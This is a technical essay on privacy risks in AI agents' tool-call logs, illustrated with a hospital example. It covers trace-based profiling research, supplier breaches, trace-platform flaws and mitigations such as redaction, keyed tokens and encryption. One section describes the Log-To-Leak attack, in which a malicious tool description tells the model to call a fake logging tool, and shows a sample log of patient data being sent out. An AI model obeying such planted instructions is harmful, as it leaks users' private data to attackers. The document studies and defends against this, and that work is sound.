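A log stripped of tool names, arguments and results still records when each call was made. From a few weeks of these times, a thief could learn that the hospital exports its bills at two in the morning, when a large transfer would attract little attention. If the log includes approvals, it also shows which clerk approves emails within a second and when nobody is on duty to approve anything.

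The order and timing of calls can indicate what a case is about. Nguyen and colleagues describe a diagnostic system in which specialised agents share a workspace. If the cardiology agent becomes active after the radiology agent but before the pathology agent, an observer can infer the probable category of diagnosis without reading any content. In their business example, several companies share one tracing system. If one company's legal and financial agents suddenly start working at the same times, another customer who can see the timestamps might suspect that the company is preparing an acquisition. Nguyen and colleagues base both examples on how such systems work and do not test them in the paper.

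### How much a model can guess about a user

The clearest measurement of what tool calls reveal about the people behind them comes from PrivacyTrace, a test introduced by Duan, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Much Can Tool Calls Reveal About You?* It works in four steps:

1. The researchers generated 1,000 fictional people whose characteristics match population statistics for 26 countries. Each person has 17 attributes. Thirteen are traits such as age, religion, income and health conditions, and four are identifiers (name, email address, phone number and government number).
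2. A model wrote four tasks for each person, one each in travel, health, shopping and career learning. The tasks fit the person's profile but leave out identifiers and unrelated sensitive facts.
3. The model then played the person in a conversation with an agent, which used real tools from 25 MCP servers. This produced 4,000 runs with 67,950 tool calls.
4. An attacking model received the tool calls from a run, without the conversation, and had to guess all 17 attributes.

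For comparison, the attacking model also guessed without any tool calls, knowing only which attributes to fill in.

| What the attacking model received | Attributes guessed correctly |
|---|---|
| No tool calls | 17.97% |
| Metadata (such as tool names) and order | 14.53% |
| Metadata, order and results | 24.54% |
| Metadata, order and arguments | 27.71% |
| Complete trace of one task | 26.25% |
| Complete traces of one person's four tasks, linked together | 32.77% |

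The complete trace of one task raised the attack's average score by about eight percentage points. The gain was larger when the score excluded the four identifiers, which the attack almost never recovered. On the remaining items, the attacking model was right about 34% of the time with a trace and at most 23.5% without one. It guessed citizenship correctly in 57.73% of cases and religion in 50.03%. Guessing China, the most common country in the sample, for everyone would have been right only about a quarter of the time.

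The attack scored slightly lower when it used results as well as arguments. Duan and colleagues suggest that results often contain alternatives that don't describe the user, such as flights the person never booked. An organisation that stops logging results but keeps logging arguments would therefore gain no protection against this kind of profiling, although it would keep many whole records out of the log.

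The services that revealed the most in the attack included some that look innocuous, such as geocoding (turning an address into coordinates), flight search, web search, weather and time services. In the paper's opening example, a person's preferred travel times and means of transport, together with the places the agent looks up, may point to a religion or a health condition.

The attack recovered only 35 of 16,000 identifiers: 34 names, one phone number, and no email addresses or government numbers. The tasks deliberately left identifiers out, so the result shows only that a model can rarely guess a name that nobody typed. The hospital's agent, however, has to put Mrs Keller's name or patient number into an argument to look her up, and a thief who has the arguments can read it there.

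Profiling a trace is cheap. DeepSeek-V4-Flash, the main attacking model, processed the 4,000 traces for $46.49, or about a cent each. GPT-5.5 cost $1,079.88 and scored 27.78%, only slightly better. The guesses are unreliable, though. When the researchers had the attacking model first pick out the attributes that the trace supported, it chose 17% of the attributes and was right about 46% of the time. A thief who used these guesses to find patients with a particular illness would often pick the wrong people, which could harm them as well as the patients correctly identified.

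The results may not apply to real users. A model given the person's full profile wrote each task, so the tasks may contain more clues than real requests do. The same model, DeepSeek-V4-Flash, also played the user, ran the agent and made most of the guesses. Its guesses could have relied on the same stereotypes it used to write the tasks, such as what a religious person would ask for. But three models from other companies scored between 25.29% and 28.32% on the same traces, so one model's stereotypes probably don't explain much of the result.

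### Why tool names can still be secret

Guessing from metadata and order alone scored 14.53%, lower than guessing without seeing any tool calls. This does not show that an organisation can safely publish its tool names.

The attacking model could have scored about 18% by ignoring the metadata. It did worse, so the extra text hurt its performance. The score therefore measures how well this model used the metadata in this test, and the metadata may contain more information than the score shows. The score is also an average over 17 attributes, which could hide gains on a few of them.

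The choice of tools matters more. The servers in PrivacyTrace offered general services, such as weather and web search, that people of any religion or income might use. The names of such tools reveal little about any one user, but a specialised tool's name can be almost as informative as the record itself. Suppose that the hospital is treating 2,000 of its 200,000 patients for cancer, and that 95% of the patients whom agents look up in the oncology registry have cancer. A patient chosen at random has a 1% chance of having cancer. That chance rises to 95% if an observer can link one `query_oncology_registry` call to the patient, perhaps through the time of an appointment.

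PrivacyTrace also tested only personal attributes of the user. An intelligence service that obtained a defence body's log would want to know other things, such as whether the body can track a certain type of submarine or which projects have started since last year. It could learn some of this from a list of tool names, without linking any call to a person. Similarly, a competitor that found `predict_toxicity_kx12` in a drug company's log could learn the internal name of an unannounced compound. No experiment described here has measured this kind of leak, which would vary with how an organisation names its tools. Until one does, organisations that run classified or proprietary systems have good reason to treat tool names as sensitive.

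### What observers can infer without the log

The company that runs a tool server sees every call to that server and can keep a record of them, so a thief may not need the organisation's log. In PrivacyTrace, an observer who saw only one server's calls guessed 24.24% of attributes correctly. An observer who saw the whole task guessed 27.33% correctly for the same set of cases, so one server's calls contained most of the useful evidence. Linking a user's tasks gave the highest score in the experiment, and a gateway or an observability vendor is well placed to do that.

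Duan and colleagues also describe three earlier attacks. One of them, IntentMiner (Yao and colleagues, 2025), reconstructs a user's current request, rather than lasting traits, from the content of MCP tool calls. A server that received `patient: "P-118204"` and a date range could use this method to try to work out why the clerk wanted the record, even though it never received the clerk's words.

The other two attacks use network traffic. Encryption hides the contents of a message, but an internet provider can still see when a computer sends data, how much it sends and usually which service it contacts. Jeong and colleagues (2025) used the sites that web and research agents contacted, and the timing of those visits, to infer users' prompts and lasting traits. AgentPrint, by Zhang and colleagues (2025), uses patterns in encrypted traffic to identify what an agent is doing and infer attributes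 of its user.

Restricting access to the tool-call log does not hide the agent's activity from people who can observe its network traffic. A hospital's firewall and proxy logs, for example, contain much of the same information, and more staff may be able to read them. If the hospital's agent contacts a genetic-testing laboratory a few minutes after each appointment at a particular clinic, the network team could work out which patients are having tests without opening the tool-call log.

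## How tool-call logs reach outsiders

In autumn 2026, Cursor, Notion and Warp disclosed that outsiders had accessed records of their users' work with AI agents or assistants. All three traced the breach to a supplier. Records can also leak through flaws in the platforms that store them, malicious tools that get an agent to report on its own work, and copies that an organisation's staff make during ordinary work.

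### Theft through a supplier

The fullest public account comes from Cursor, which makes a code editor with a built-in agent. Cursor's *An update on our recent security incident* describes a chain of events that began with a log and ended with malicious software:

1. Cursor had given Fireworks, a company that trains and runs AI models, a key to a storage area containing traces from its coding agent. Fireworks exposed the key.
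2. An attacker used the key to copy the traces. Most dated from 2025, and all came from sessions outside Cursor's Privacy Mode, which Cursor was permitted to use for training models.
3. A few traces contained credentials that nobody had removed. Starting with these, the attacker got into some of the online services that Cursor uses.
4. There the attacker reached archived source code, customer support emails, summaries of some agent conversations and more credentials, which users had sent to the support team.
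5. On 29 October the attacker used a stolen credential to place malicious copies of the Claude Code extension where Cursor's users download extensions. They stayed there for about 11 hours, and up to 5,000 users may have received one.

Cursor says that the theft exposed traces from fewer than 0.05% of the users who did not use Privacy Mode, and API credentials from less than 0.01% of customers. The key to the storage area was read-only, so the attacker could not change anything there. These limits helped little, because a few working passwords were enough to reach other systems.

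In its statement, Cursor doesn't say when the attacker copied the traces or whose credentials gave access to Cursor's own services. A customer's key would not normally give that access, so some of the traces may have come from Cursor's staff. If the credentials were in the 2025 traces, they still worked at least nine months later.

Notion, which makes software for shared notes and documents, lost data through the same supplier. It had used Fireworks to classify users' AI chats for a feature that shows customers how their staff use AI. Notion's *Fireworks AI incident* (2026) reports that the stolen data included chat transcripts and that under 1% of workspaces were affected. The transcripts contained no tool results, and for most workspaces they had no label showing who wrote them. But unlabelled text can still identify people. If a hospital billing clerk had typed "Maria Keller, born 8 March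 1961" into such a chat, the transcript would have identified the patient even with the clerk's and hospital's names removed.

Fireworks had promised in its contract to keep no data, according to KIberblick's *Notion-AI-Chats beim Fireworks-Angriff erbeutet* (2026), which quotes Notion's later finding that "data was retained from the Fireworks endpoints that we used". But Fireworks says that its inference service, which runs models on request, keeps nothing by default, and that it has no evidence of leaked prompts or outputs (杨, *Fireworks AI更新安全事件通报*, 2026). Both accounts could be true if Fireworks counts the files for Notion's classification work separately from live requests, but that is a guess. A hospital can rarely check a zero-retention promise before something goes wrong, because the promise concerns computers the hospital doesn't control.

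Greig (2026), in *AI company Fireworks says hackers stole data, billing info during October breaches*, reports that Fireworks had two breaches in October. In the second, attackers got in through an outside cloud provider that hosted Fireworks' development machines. If they took Notion's transcripts in that breach, the attack started at a company three contracts away from Notion's customers.

Information about the theft also passed slowly along this chain. Fireworks first told Notion about stolen data on 2 November, and Notion found only artificial test data in what Fireworks had identified. On 4 November Notion deleted everything it had stored at Fireworks, but this could protect only against future thefts. Two days later Fireworks warned that the attackers might have taken customer data, and it confirmed the full set of stolen data on 8 November.

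In both cases the stolen records were second copies, which neither company needed for answering users' requests. Cursor had kept its traces for training and historical analysis, and Notion had sent its transcripts away to produce usage statistics.

Much less is public about Warp, which began as a terminal (a program for typing commands) and is now a workspace for coding agents. Its chief executive, Zach Lloyd, said that attackers had exploited a vendor in Warp's infrastructure and that roughly 1% of users may be affected. Bot Mutiny's *Warp Vendor Attack Exposed AI Agent Logs and Telemetry* (2026) summarises these statements from a report by the news site BleepingComputer. Antipov (2026), in *Взлом подрядчика — и журналы ИИ-агентов Warp под угрозой*, estimates that this is about 8,000 people, based on the figure of at least 800,000 users on Warp's website. The exposed records were telemetry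 (data on how people use the product) and logs of the agents' decisions.

Warp learned of the attack on 23 October and says it detected the operation within hours. It has not named the vendor or said whether the records contained source code, prompts or passwords, so the harm is hard to judge. Many of a terminal agent's tool calls are shell commands, and a log of them might contain little more than names and times, or every key that a developer typed into a command.

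Antipov also points out that, according to Warp's documentation, users can turn off analytics collection, but conversations and agent runs in Warp's cloud need stored records to work. A user who had opted out of telemetry could therefore still have had logs there.

The thieves may have wanted credentials for AI models rather than the logs. In *“Black October” for AI Developer Platforms*, Read and McCarthy (2026), who work for the security company Wiz, list nine AI developer platforms, including Warp and Fireworks, that disclosed incidents in October. They added three more in early November. Most of the companies had published few technical details, but public reports described attackers searching for stored environment variables, especially those that give access to AI models. Criminals can resell that access.

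Wiz observed the use of one key stolen from a vendor. Somebody tested it within 30 minutes of the reported theft. Over the next four days there were only occasional calls, apparently to check that the key still worked. The thieves then made about 800,000 model calls in 30 hours, until somebody shut off the key. The customer could have replaced the key during those four days, provided that the vendor had warned it and it knew which keys the vendor held.

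Thieves who want keys have a reason to copy any log that might contain them, and they also take any patient data in that log.

An observability vendor can also store customers' keys separately from their traces. Braintrust, which stores traces and helps customers evaluate their AI systems, keeps the keys they use to access model providers. In May 2026 intruders got into one of its Amazon cloud accounts, which probably gave them access to those keys. SecurityWeek's *AI Firm Braintrust Prompts API Key Rotation After Data Breach* reports that Braintrust learned of the problem on 4 May, after someone reported suspicious behaviour, and emailed its customers the next day. Braintrust confirmed that the breach had affected one customer, and three others reported suspicious jumps in their use of AI models.

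Only the keys are known to have been exposed. SecurityWeek does not report any theft of traces, but Braintrust was still investigating at the time, and it is unclear how the intruders got in. Jaime Blasco of Nudge Security told SecurityWeek that every such tool "becomes a credential warehouse". His company sells security software, so he has an interest in the warning, but the Braintrust case supports it. A hospital that gives one vendor both its traces and its model keys makes that vendor a more valuable target for attackers.

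### Flaws in the platforms that store traces

Known thefts are only part of the risk, because a platform can have a serious flaw that nobody exploits. CVE, the public catalogue of software flaws, has entries for three products that either store traces or send data to products that do. An entry shows that an attacker could have got in, but it is not evidence that anyone did.

The flaw in LangSmith, CVE-2026-25750, let an attacker take over a user's account. One part of the product let a web link set which server the user's browser contacted, without checking that the address was safe. If a logged-in developer at the hospital had opened a link prepared by an attacker, the browser would have sent the developer's login token to the attacker's server. The attacker could then have used the token to read the traces the developer was allowed to read, including the arguments and results of tool calls.

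LiteLLM, a gateway for calls to language models, can send a record of each call to the trace store Langfuse, for which it needs Langfuse's keys. In LiteLLM version 1.52.1, an error while reading a team's settings could expose those keys (CVE-2025-0330). Anyone who obtained them could open the Langfuse project and all of its stored requests. Because the fault was in the gateway and the keys were valid, securing Langfuse itself would not have prevented this access.

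A flaw in Langfuse, CVE-2026-41487, exposed keys to members with low privileges. The damage from such a flaw depends on what the key is for. A key for a model provider lets its holder run up bills, while a key for a trace project may let its holder read the traces. At the hospital, the low-privileged member might be a contractor invited to look at a single dashboard.

Encrypting the stored traces would not have stopped an attacker who used a stolen token or key, because the platform decrypts the data for anyone with valid credentials. The platform's access log might also record the attacker's activity as a developer reading traces.

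### A tool that poses as a logger

An attacker can also try to make the agent send out the record. Hu, Fan and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Log-To-Leak*. The attacker runs an MCP server that offers a harmless tool and a second tool presented as a logging tool. The harmless tool's description contains an instruction to call the logging tool at the end of each task. Because the harness sends tool descriptions to the model, the model reads this instruction even if the user never asks for either tool.

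The instruction has four parts: when to make the call, which tool to use, an official-sounding reason, and a statement that the step is compulsory. An instruction that only named the tool rarely worked. Placing the instruction in the tool's description worked better than placing it in the tool's name, an argument's name or an argument's default value.

Suppose that the hospital has enabled an outside server that formats invoices, and a clerk asks which treatment invoice 60713 covers. With a successful attack, the log would look like this:

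```
10:05:28  query_oncology_registry
  arguments  patient: "P-118204"
  result     diagnosis: "C50.9", treatment: "chemotherapy, 4 sessions"

10:05:33  record_activity
  arguments  request: "Which treatment does invoice 60713 cover?",
             server: "oncology-registry",
             response: "diagnosis: C50.9, ...",
             answer: "The invoice covers four sessions..."
  result     status: "saved"
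```

The clerk gets a correct answer. Without ever having had access to the registry, the attacker obtains the four items that Hu and colleagues set out to steal: the user's request, the name of the last server used, that server's response and the agent's answer.

The researchers ran the attack on agents that used five MCP servers: GitHub (software projects), Mapbox (maps), PayPal (payments), YFinance (market data) and Playwright (web browser control). They wrote 160 task prompts each for GitHub, Mapbox and PayPal with GPT-4o's help, and took 40 for YFinance and 35 for Playwright from an existing benchmark. The four models were GPT-4o (released in May 2024), Claude Sonnet 4 (May 2025), GPT-5 (August 2025) and GPT-OSS-120B (August 2025).

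| Measure | Result |
|---|---|
| Pairs of model and server in which the tools worked properly | 18 of 20 |
| Runs in which the agent made the extra call | 62.64% to 100%, depending on the pair |
| Accuracy of the copied data when it did | 76.55% to 95.64% |
| Change in how often the agent completed the user's task | At most 6.63 percentage points in 16 of the 18 pairs |

A team that checks only whether its agent still does its job would therefore usually miss the attack. Users might still notice it, because some products display each tool call as it happens.

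With GPT-4o on the GitHub server, the attack still succeeded in more than 55% of runs against three of the defences. A detector that looks for instructions hidden in tool descriptions flagged 85.53% of harmless descriptions, so an organisation that relied on it would reject most harmless tools.

All four models are more than a year old, and newer ones may resist the attack better. The attack also works only if the organisation has enabled the attacker's server, the model can see the server's descriptions, and the harness lets the model call the logging tool without separate permission. The last condition is the easiest for a hospital to change, and Hu and colleagues conclude that the host software should authorise such additional calls itself.

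A hospital could go further and refuse every logging tool that the model has to call. The hospital would lose little, because its harness or gateway already records tool calls without the model's help. A sequence rule that treats outside tool servers like outside email addresses would also catch the example above, because the agent sends patient data to the attacker five seconds after reading it. Without such a rule, an analyst who sees a tool called `record_activity` in the log may mistake it for part of the hospital's own monitoring.

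### Copies made by an organisation's own staff

Some exposures begin without an attacker, when a developer turns on content capture to find a fault and leaves it on, or when a program writes more to a debug file than anyone remembers.

Hermes Agent, an open-source agent from Nous Research, had a problem of the second kind in October 2026. According to a notice on its public issue tracker, users who exported their profiles could also be exporting debug files. The agent wrote these files when a request to a model failed, and each contained the whole web request, including the login key in readable form. The export function left out password files, ordinary logs and session transcripts, but not the debug files. Anyone who shared such an export could have shared a working key. Hermes now masks the key before it writes the file.

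An agent can also publish a copy of a log on its own. Coding agents left 13,000 company screenshots in public repositories. These were the agents' output, not part of a log, but an agent's trace may contain the same images, and an organisation that keeps traces beside its source code could publish both by the same mistake.

Logs can also reach outsiders through support requests. When a tool call fails, the quickest way to explain the problem is to attach the trace to a support ticket, which has its own readers and retention period. In the Cursor case, the attacker found credentials in support messages, in a system unrelated to trace storage.

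There is little public evidence about excessive staff access to agent logs. An employee who reads a trace out of curiosity causes no malfunction, and a patient whose data is in the trace is unlikely to find out. Giving more people access also increases the risk from outsiders, because an attacker who takes over any of their accounts can read the same traces, as the LangSmith flaw illustrates.

### One diagnosis in eight places

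Mrs Keller's diagnosis code, C50.9, belongs in the oncology registry. Suppose an agent answers her insurer, and the harness records the arguments, results and model inputs from that run. The hospital sends its traces to an observability vendor. The gateway also records results and forwards its entries to the SIEM. A week later, a developer investigating a slow call attaches the exported run to a support ticket and saves it as a test case. The retention periods here are invented, except for the model provider's 30 days.

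| Place | How the code gets there | Copies after two weeks | Time until deletion |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harness's trace store | Once as a result, twice in model inputs | 3 | 90 days |
| Model provider | Two model inputs | 2 | Up to 30 days |
| Observability vendor | Export of the trace | 3 | 180 days |
| Gateway log | Result of the registry call | 1 | 90 days |
| SIEM | Forwarded gateway entry | 1 | One year |
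| Backups of the trace store | A full backup every night, each kept for 14 days | 42 | 14 days after the last backup that contains the run |
| Support ticket | Attached export | 3 | No date set |
| Developer's test case | Saved export | 3 | No date set |

That makes 58 copies of a code that the agent needed once. The total excludes the email, which describes the treatment in words, and any copies in the vendor's own backups.

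The number of places matters more than the number of copies. Even if the registry admits only 40 clinicians, that restriction applies to none of the eight. Developers can read the trace store, security analysts can read the SIEM, and support staff at another company can read the ticket. A thief needs access to only one of them, and the hospital might then have to tell Mrs Keller about a breach in a system her doctors have never heard of.

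If the harness had not recorded content, 54 of the 58 copies of the code would not exist. These are the copies in the trace store, its backups, the ticket and the test case, and those held by the vendor. The other four, in the systems of the model provider, the gateway and the SIEM, would remain because the harness's recording setting does not affect them.

Deleting the run later works less well because copies remain elsewhere. After the trace store deletes it at 90 days, the last backup keeps it for up to two more weeks, the vendor for about three more months and the SIEM for about nine more. The ticket and the test case also contain the patient's diagnosis, and they remain until somebody remembers this and deletes them.

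## Recording less while keeping the evidence

Most of the 58 copies of Mrs Keller's diagnosis exist because the harness wrote the full text of each result into its log. The hospital could store something less revealing instead. For the patient number in the call to `query_oncology_registry`, its options include these (the hashes and tokens here are invented and shortened):

| Technique | What the log stores for `patient: "P-118204"` |
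|---|---|
| Content capture off | Nothing |
| Redaction | `patient: [PATIENT]` |
| Plain hash | `patient: 5d1e07` |
| Keyed token | `patient: 9f2c4a` |
| Derived fact | `patient matches invoice: yes` |
| Encryption | Unreadable bytes and a reference to a key |

### Switching content capture off

With content capture off, staff can still count calls, find slow tools and notice a burst of registry queries at night, but they can't tell which patients the agent looked up or check any rule that depends on the missing fields.

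The setting fails if another recording path, such as the gateway or a debug file, stays active. Products also differ in what they keep. PegasusAI Studio stores tool arguments only for users who opt in, while Anthropic's Compliance API includes tool inputs in its transcripts, up to a size limit.

The hospital can test its own settings with a fictitious patient. A staff member asks the agent to look her up and send an email about her, then searches every log, backup and vendor dashboard for her name, number and diagnosis. The test is worth repeating after each update, because updates can change default settings.

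### Redaction

Redaction software searches the full text for sensitive items and replaces each with a placeholder. Investigators can then read what the agent did without seeing whom it involved. Numbered placeholders, such as [PATIENT-1] and [PATIENT-2], also let them tell whether two calls in a run concerned the same person. *When Only the Final Text Survives* reports that attributing text to agents worked almost as well after placeholders replaced names, email addresses and phone numbers.

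The simplest redactors search for patterns, such as "P-" followed by six digits. *Redacting Personal Data* (2026) describes this method as fast and predictable but unable to find names that were not specified in advance. Tools that use a language-processing model can find such names, but they need more computing time and take seconds to load.

Where the data has named fields, the harness can delete the `patient` argument without having to recognise its value as sensitive, but the same value may still appear elsewhere. *Auditing Tool Traces in Agentic LLMs* (2026) gives an example from protein research, in which one tool returned a structure's identifier in its own field and another included it in a filename. Redacting only that field would have left the identifier in the filename.

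*Separating Disclosure from Authorization* (2026), which describes a system for approving and recording agents' actions, reports a similar failure. One of the system's rules replaced an identifier in a file path only if that part of the path was entirely numeric or had a standard format. The rule left `patient-record-778812` intact because the number was attached to words. A test that searched the whole output for the identifier caught the fault. The developers then removed the last part of every path, where names and record numbers usually appear. This fix doesn't depend on anticipating every format, but it means their policies can no longer distinguish one type of file from another.

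Even a very accurate redactor will often leave something behind in a long trace. If it catches 99% of sensitive items and its misses are independent, the chance that it clears all of 100 items is:

*0.99^100 ≈ 0.37*

So about 63% of such traces would still contain at least one item. To remove all 100 items from 95% of traces, the redactor would have to catch about 99.95% of them. Misses are probably not independent, however. A redactor that fails to recognise an unusual surname may miss it all 20 times it appears, so missed items would be concentrated in fewer traces, with more in each.

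Detectors' measured accuracy is often far below 99%. *REDACT* (Vats, Agrawal and colleagues, 2026) tested five detectors on 1,000 synthetic records in 25 languages. Its high-sensitivity group includes health data, religion, criminal offences and dates of birth.

| Detector | Share of high-sensitivity items found |
|---|---|
| Presidio (Microsoft's tool, which combines patterns with a language-processing model) | 7% |
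| GLiNER | 42% |
| OpenAI Privacy Filter | 57% |
| GPT-4.1 | 74% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 77% |

A detector that finds each item 77% of the time would find all of ten items only about 7% of the time. Newer models may do better. Human annotators disagreed noticeably about which items were highly sensitive, so small differences between detectors mean little. *RedactionBench* (2026), a test on 200 documents, likewise found no near-perfect redactor. The best systems, leading models with tools, scored an average of 0.71.

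Results can be much better on familiar material. *AnonLFI 2.0* (2025) reports that an earlier version of its software found 97.38% of the sensitive items in 763 real security incidents handled by Brazilian response teams, with no false detections. Like Presidio, that version combined patterns with a language-processing model. The gap between 7% and 97% suggests that the text matters at least as much as the tool, so a hospital should test a redactor on its own logs before relying on it.

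There is little evidence from agents' own traces. In *RedAct*, Xu, He and Fung (2026) tried to remove trade know-how, such as formulas and thresholds, from traces of 75 specialised tasks, then tested whether other agents could learn it from the traces. Agents that learned from the raw traces gained 44.7% to 67.1% of the improvement that the original know-how provides. Agents that learned from the redacted traces did slightly worse than agents with no know-how. The researchers report that the redacted traces kept the evidence needed for an audit. However, the redactor knew what to look for because it had the documents that contained the secrets. A hospital's redactor usually has no such reference for the contents of an email.

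*Soei* (2026) examined 45 sessions of agents writing software and found strings resembling credentials in 1,326 records from 16 of them. Tool arguments accounted for 628 of these records and the agents' own messages for 654. A second log of the same sessions, filtered before storage, contained no such strings. This is good evidence for filtering before storage, but a search for credential patterns can't find passwords that look like ordinary words. None of these studies measured how much personal data a redactor misses in real tool-call traces.

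Redacting messages after they are stored leaves the original text in the first log and its backups. OpenTelemetry allows earlier redaction because its upload routine can modify messages before the software records them on a span. The redactor should also run on the hospital's own machines because, as *SurrogateShield* (2026) points out, a cloud redaction service has to receive the text it is supposed to protect.

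### Plain hashes

If the log stores a plain hash of the patient number instead of the number itself, an investigator can still see that two calls concerned the same patient, because equal inputs give equal hashes. The investigator can also check whether a known patient appears by hashing her number and searching for the result. However, someone who steals the log can recover the patient numbers by hashing every possible number and looking for matches.

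A nine-digit identity number has a billion possible values. A thief who can compute ten billion hashes a second would need:

*10^9 / 10^10 = 0.1 seconds*

to try them all. Mrs Keller's six-digit patient number would take a ten-thousandth of a second. Adding a random value, or salt, to each number and storing it in the log would prevent the thief from using one precomputed table for the whole log. It would still take only a tenth of a second to break each entry. A deliberately slow hash function that allows 10,000 guesses a second would extend the search for a nine-digit number to about 28 hours, which is a delay rather than real protection.

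The earlier version of AnonLFI had this weakness because it used hashes without a secret key. It also shortened the hashes to ten characters, so two values could share one pseudonym. If the characters were hexadecimal, the chance of at least one clash would be about 2% among 200,000 patients and 37% among a million values.

The log in *Separating Disclosure from Authorization* leaves out identifying arguments but stores an unkeyed hash of the complete set, so that an auditor with a candidate set can confirm that it matches. Someone who steals the log can use the same check to guess the missing arguments. If a registry query contains only a patient number and a start date within the past year, there are about 365 million combinations, which take 0.04 seconds to test. A hash of a long email is much safer, because nobody can list every possible email. But a thief can also guess an email that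 follows a standard template in which only the name varies.

### Keyed tokens

A keyed token is also a fingerprint, but computing it requires a secret key. The harness combines the key with "P-118204" and stores the result. Without the key, a thief can't test candidate numbers.

Suppose that a hijacked agent made five registry queries, and the log contains these tokens:

```
02:11:04  query_oncology_registry   patient: 9f2c4a
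02:11:09  query_oncology_registry   patient: 71be03
02:11:15  query_oncology_registry   patient: 9f2c4a
02:11:22  query_oncology_registry   patient: c80d5e
02:11:27  query_oncology_registry   patient: 71be03
```

An investigator without the key can count three distinct tokens and infer that the agent looked up three patients. To name them, someone with the key has to compute the tokens of all 200,000 patients and find the three that match, which takes a computer less than a second. If Mrs Keller asks whether she was affected, the key holder needs to compute only her token.

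The count depends on consistent formatting. If the agent writes "P-118204" in one call and "p118204" in another, the log will contain two tokens for one patient unless the harness first converts both to the same format. Tokens also work only for values that the harness can identify, so a redactor still has to find a name inside an email's body.

Anyone who steals the key can reverse the tokens as easily as plain hashes. The harness needs the key for every call, so it is best to keep the key in a separate service that computes tokens on request and limits the number of requests. Even without the key, an employee who can both use the agent and read the log could look up a colleague, note the token that appears, and find every other call about that person.

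Stable tokens also reveal patterns. A token that appears every Monday, Wednesday and Friday might belong to a dialysis patient, and someone who knows one of the patient's appointments might recognise the token. The hospital could change the key every month to limit this, but it would then need the old keys to match a patient across months. Adding up the monthly counts would count a patient seen in both October and November twice.

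*Proteus* (Goutam, Kippen and colleagues, 2026) combines both approaches for logs on Android devices. It turns each sensitive value into a keyed token, then encrypts the token with a key that changes daily. An investigator can be given the ability to decrypt tokens for a limited period and can match events within it without seeing the original values. Storage grew by 2.41%, and the median delay was 0.2 milliseconds per message, which suggests that speed would not be the main obstacle for a hospital. The design assumes that another program has already found most of the sensitive values, and the researchers did not test it on agents.

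### Derived facts and opaque tool identifiers

Many rules can be checked with only a fact about a value, such as whether an email's recipient is outside the hospital. *Separating Disclosure from Authorization* applies this idea to each argument of a tool call. It stores a value unchanged if a rule depends on it and it doesn't identify anyone. If a rule depends on a value that does identify someone, it stores a less specific version, such as an email address's domain or whether a payee is on an approved list. It leaves out everything else, including any field that nobody has classified.

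Of the 19 fields in the developers' example set, 11 stay unchanged, six become less specific and two never leave the customer's system. These proportions depend on the developers' own rules and may be different elsewhere. A derived fact can also give away too much. For example, the domain of a small specialist clinic may reveal a patient's condition, and a long list of domains shows who the hospital deals with.

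The choice of which fields to log needs its own review. If an administrator reclassifies email subject lines as safe to store, every later subject line enters the log, and no blocked call or error message reveals the change. The system therefore lets customers set a limit on their own side that central settings can tighten but not loosen. This limit is off by default.

An organisation also can't use derived facts to answer questions that nobody anticipated. If the hospital stores only "outside" and later learns that `claims-help.example` belongs to a criminal group, it can't search old logs for that domain.

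The same idea can protect tool names. The harness replaces `query_oncology_registry` with an arbitrary label such as `tool-47`, and only a few people hold the table that translates it. Analysts can still count calls, compare sequences and run rules written by someone who has the table. But the label offers little protection if the log also contains the tool's description or a result that mentions chemotherapy. Someone who steals the log might also identify the tool if `tool-47` runs after every appointment at the cancer clinic.

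If the hospital changes the tool's name only when it writes the log, the real name still appears in MCP's web headers. The hospital could give the tool an opaque name from the start, but the model provider would still receive the description that the model needs to choose the tool. An opaque name might also cause the model to choose the wrong tool more often, so the hospital would have to test for that.

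### Encryption and the two-level store

Encrypting log entries preserves their full contents, so an investigator with the key can do whatever an unencrypted log would allow. Searching the contents or running detection rules on them also requires the key. *Agent Flight Recorder* encrypts the contents of entries by default and lets the operator disclose them one event at a time.

The hospital can encrypt the traces with a pair of keys so that a stolen login isn't enough to read them. The harness has the public key, which can only encrypt, and the hospital's privacy office has the private key, which decrypts. An attacker who takes over the harness can read new calls but not old entries. If the privacy office loses its key, the hospital can no longer read the evidence.

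A two-level store combines encryption with tokens and derived facts. For the hospital's email to Northfield, it might contain:

```
OPEN RECORD (security team and developers)
  call c-3, run r-5521, 09:14:11, clerk-204, billing-agent 4.2
  tool           send_email
  data class     patient data
  patient        9f2c4a
  recipient      outside, matches patient's insurer
  decision       allowed, no approval
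  contents       sealed record s-88310

SEALED RECORD s-88310 (opened only with approval)
  arguments and result, encrypted
```

The security team can check the rule about outside emails using the open record alone. It can also tell this email from the one to `claims-help.example`, whose recipient field would be "outside, no match". After such an alert, an analyst asks to open that one record and gives a reason, and a second person approves. The system logs the request so the hospital can later find out who read Mrs Keller's email.

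If the open records contained so little that analysts had to ask to unseal 200 records a day, the approver would probably stop reading the reasons. The hospital can use these requests to improve its log. If analysts mostly want to find out whether a recipient was an insurer, the open record should include that information. The hospital also needs an emergency procedure, perhaps one that unseals records immediately and requires a review the next day.

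OpenTelemetry's recommendation to keep content in external storage with separate access controls fits this design, but its conventions list a common way to record the references as future work. Hospitals that change vendors may therefore have to convert the links between the two levels. *Collaborative Human-Agent Protocol (CHAP)* (2026), a proposed standard for work shared by people and agents, also advises storing references, hashes and encrypted contents in permanent records instead of raw text. The draft acknowledges that it does not fully solve confidentiality.

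### Deleting contents without breaking the hash chain

If a hash chain covers Mrs Keller's diagnosis directly, removing the diagnosis makes the chain fail its check. The hospital can avoid this by chaining a fingerprint of the encrypted contents:

*h(i) = H(h(i−1), open record i, H(encrypted contents i))*

1. The harness creates a new random key for each entry and encrypts the contents with it.
2. It adds the fingerprint of the encrypted contents to the chain, together with the open record.
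3. It stores the entry's key in a separate system.
4. To erase the contents, the hospital destroys every copy of that key.

The open record and the fingerprint don't change, so the chain still passes its check. The hospital can also delete the encrypted contents and keep only their fingerprint.

This would simplify the earlier problem of the 58 copies. If the harness had encrypted everything it recorded, the copies in the trace store, its backups and the observability vendor's system would be unreadable without the keys. Destroying the keys to the three entries that contain the diagnosis would make 48 copies unreadable, including the 42 in backups. The other ten would remain readable. Six are in the support ticket and the test case, which the developer exported in readable form, and four are with the model provider, the gateway and the SIEM.

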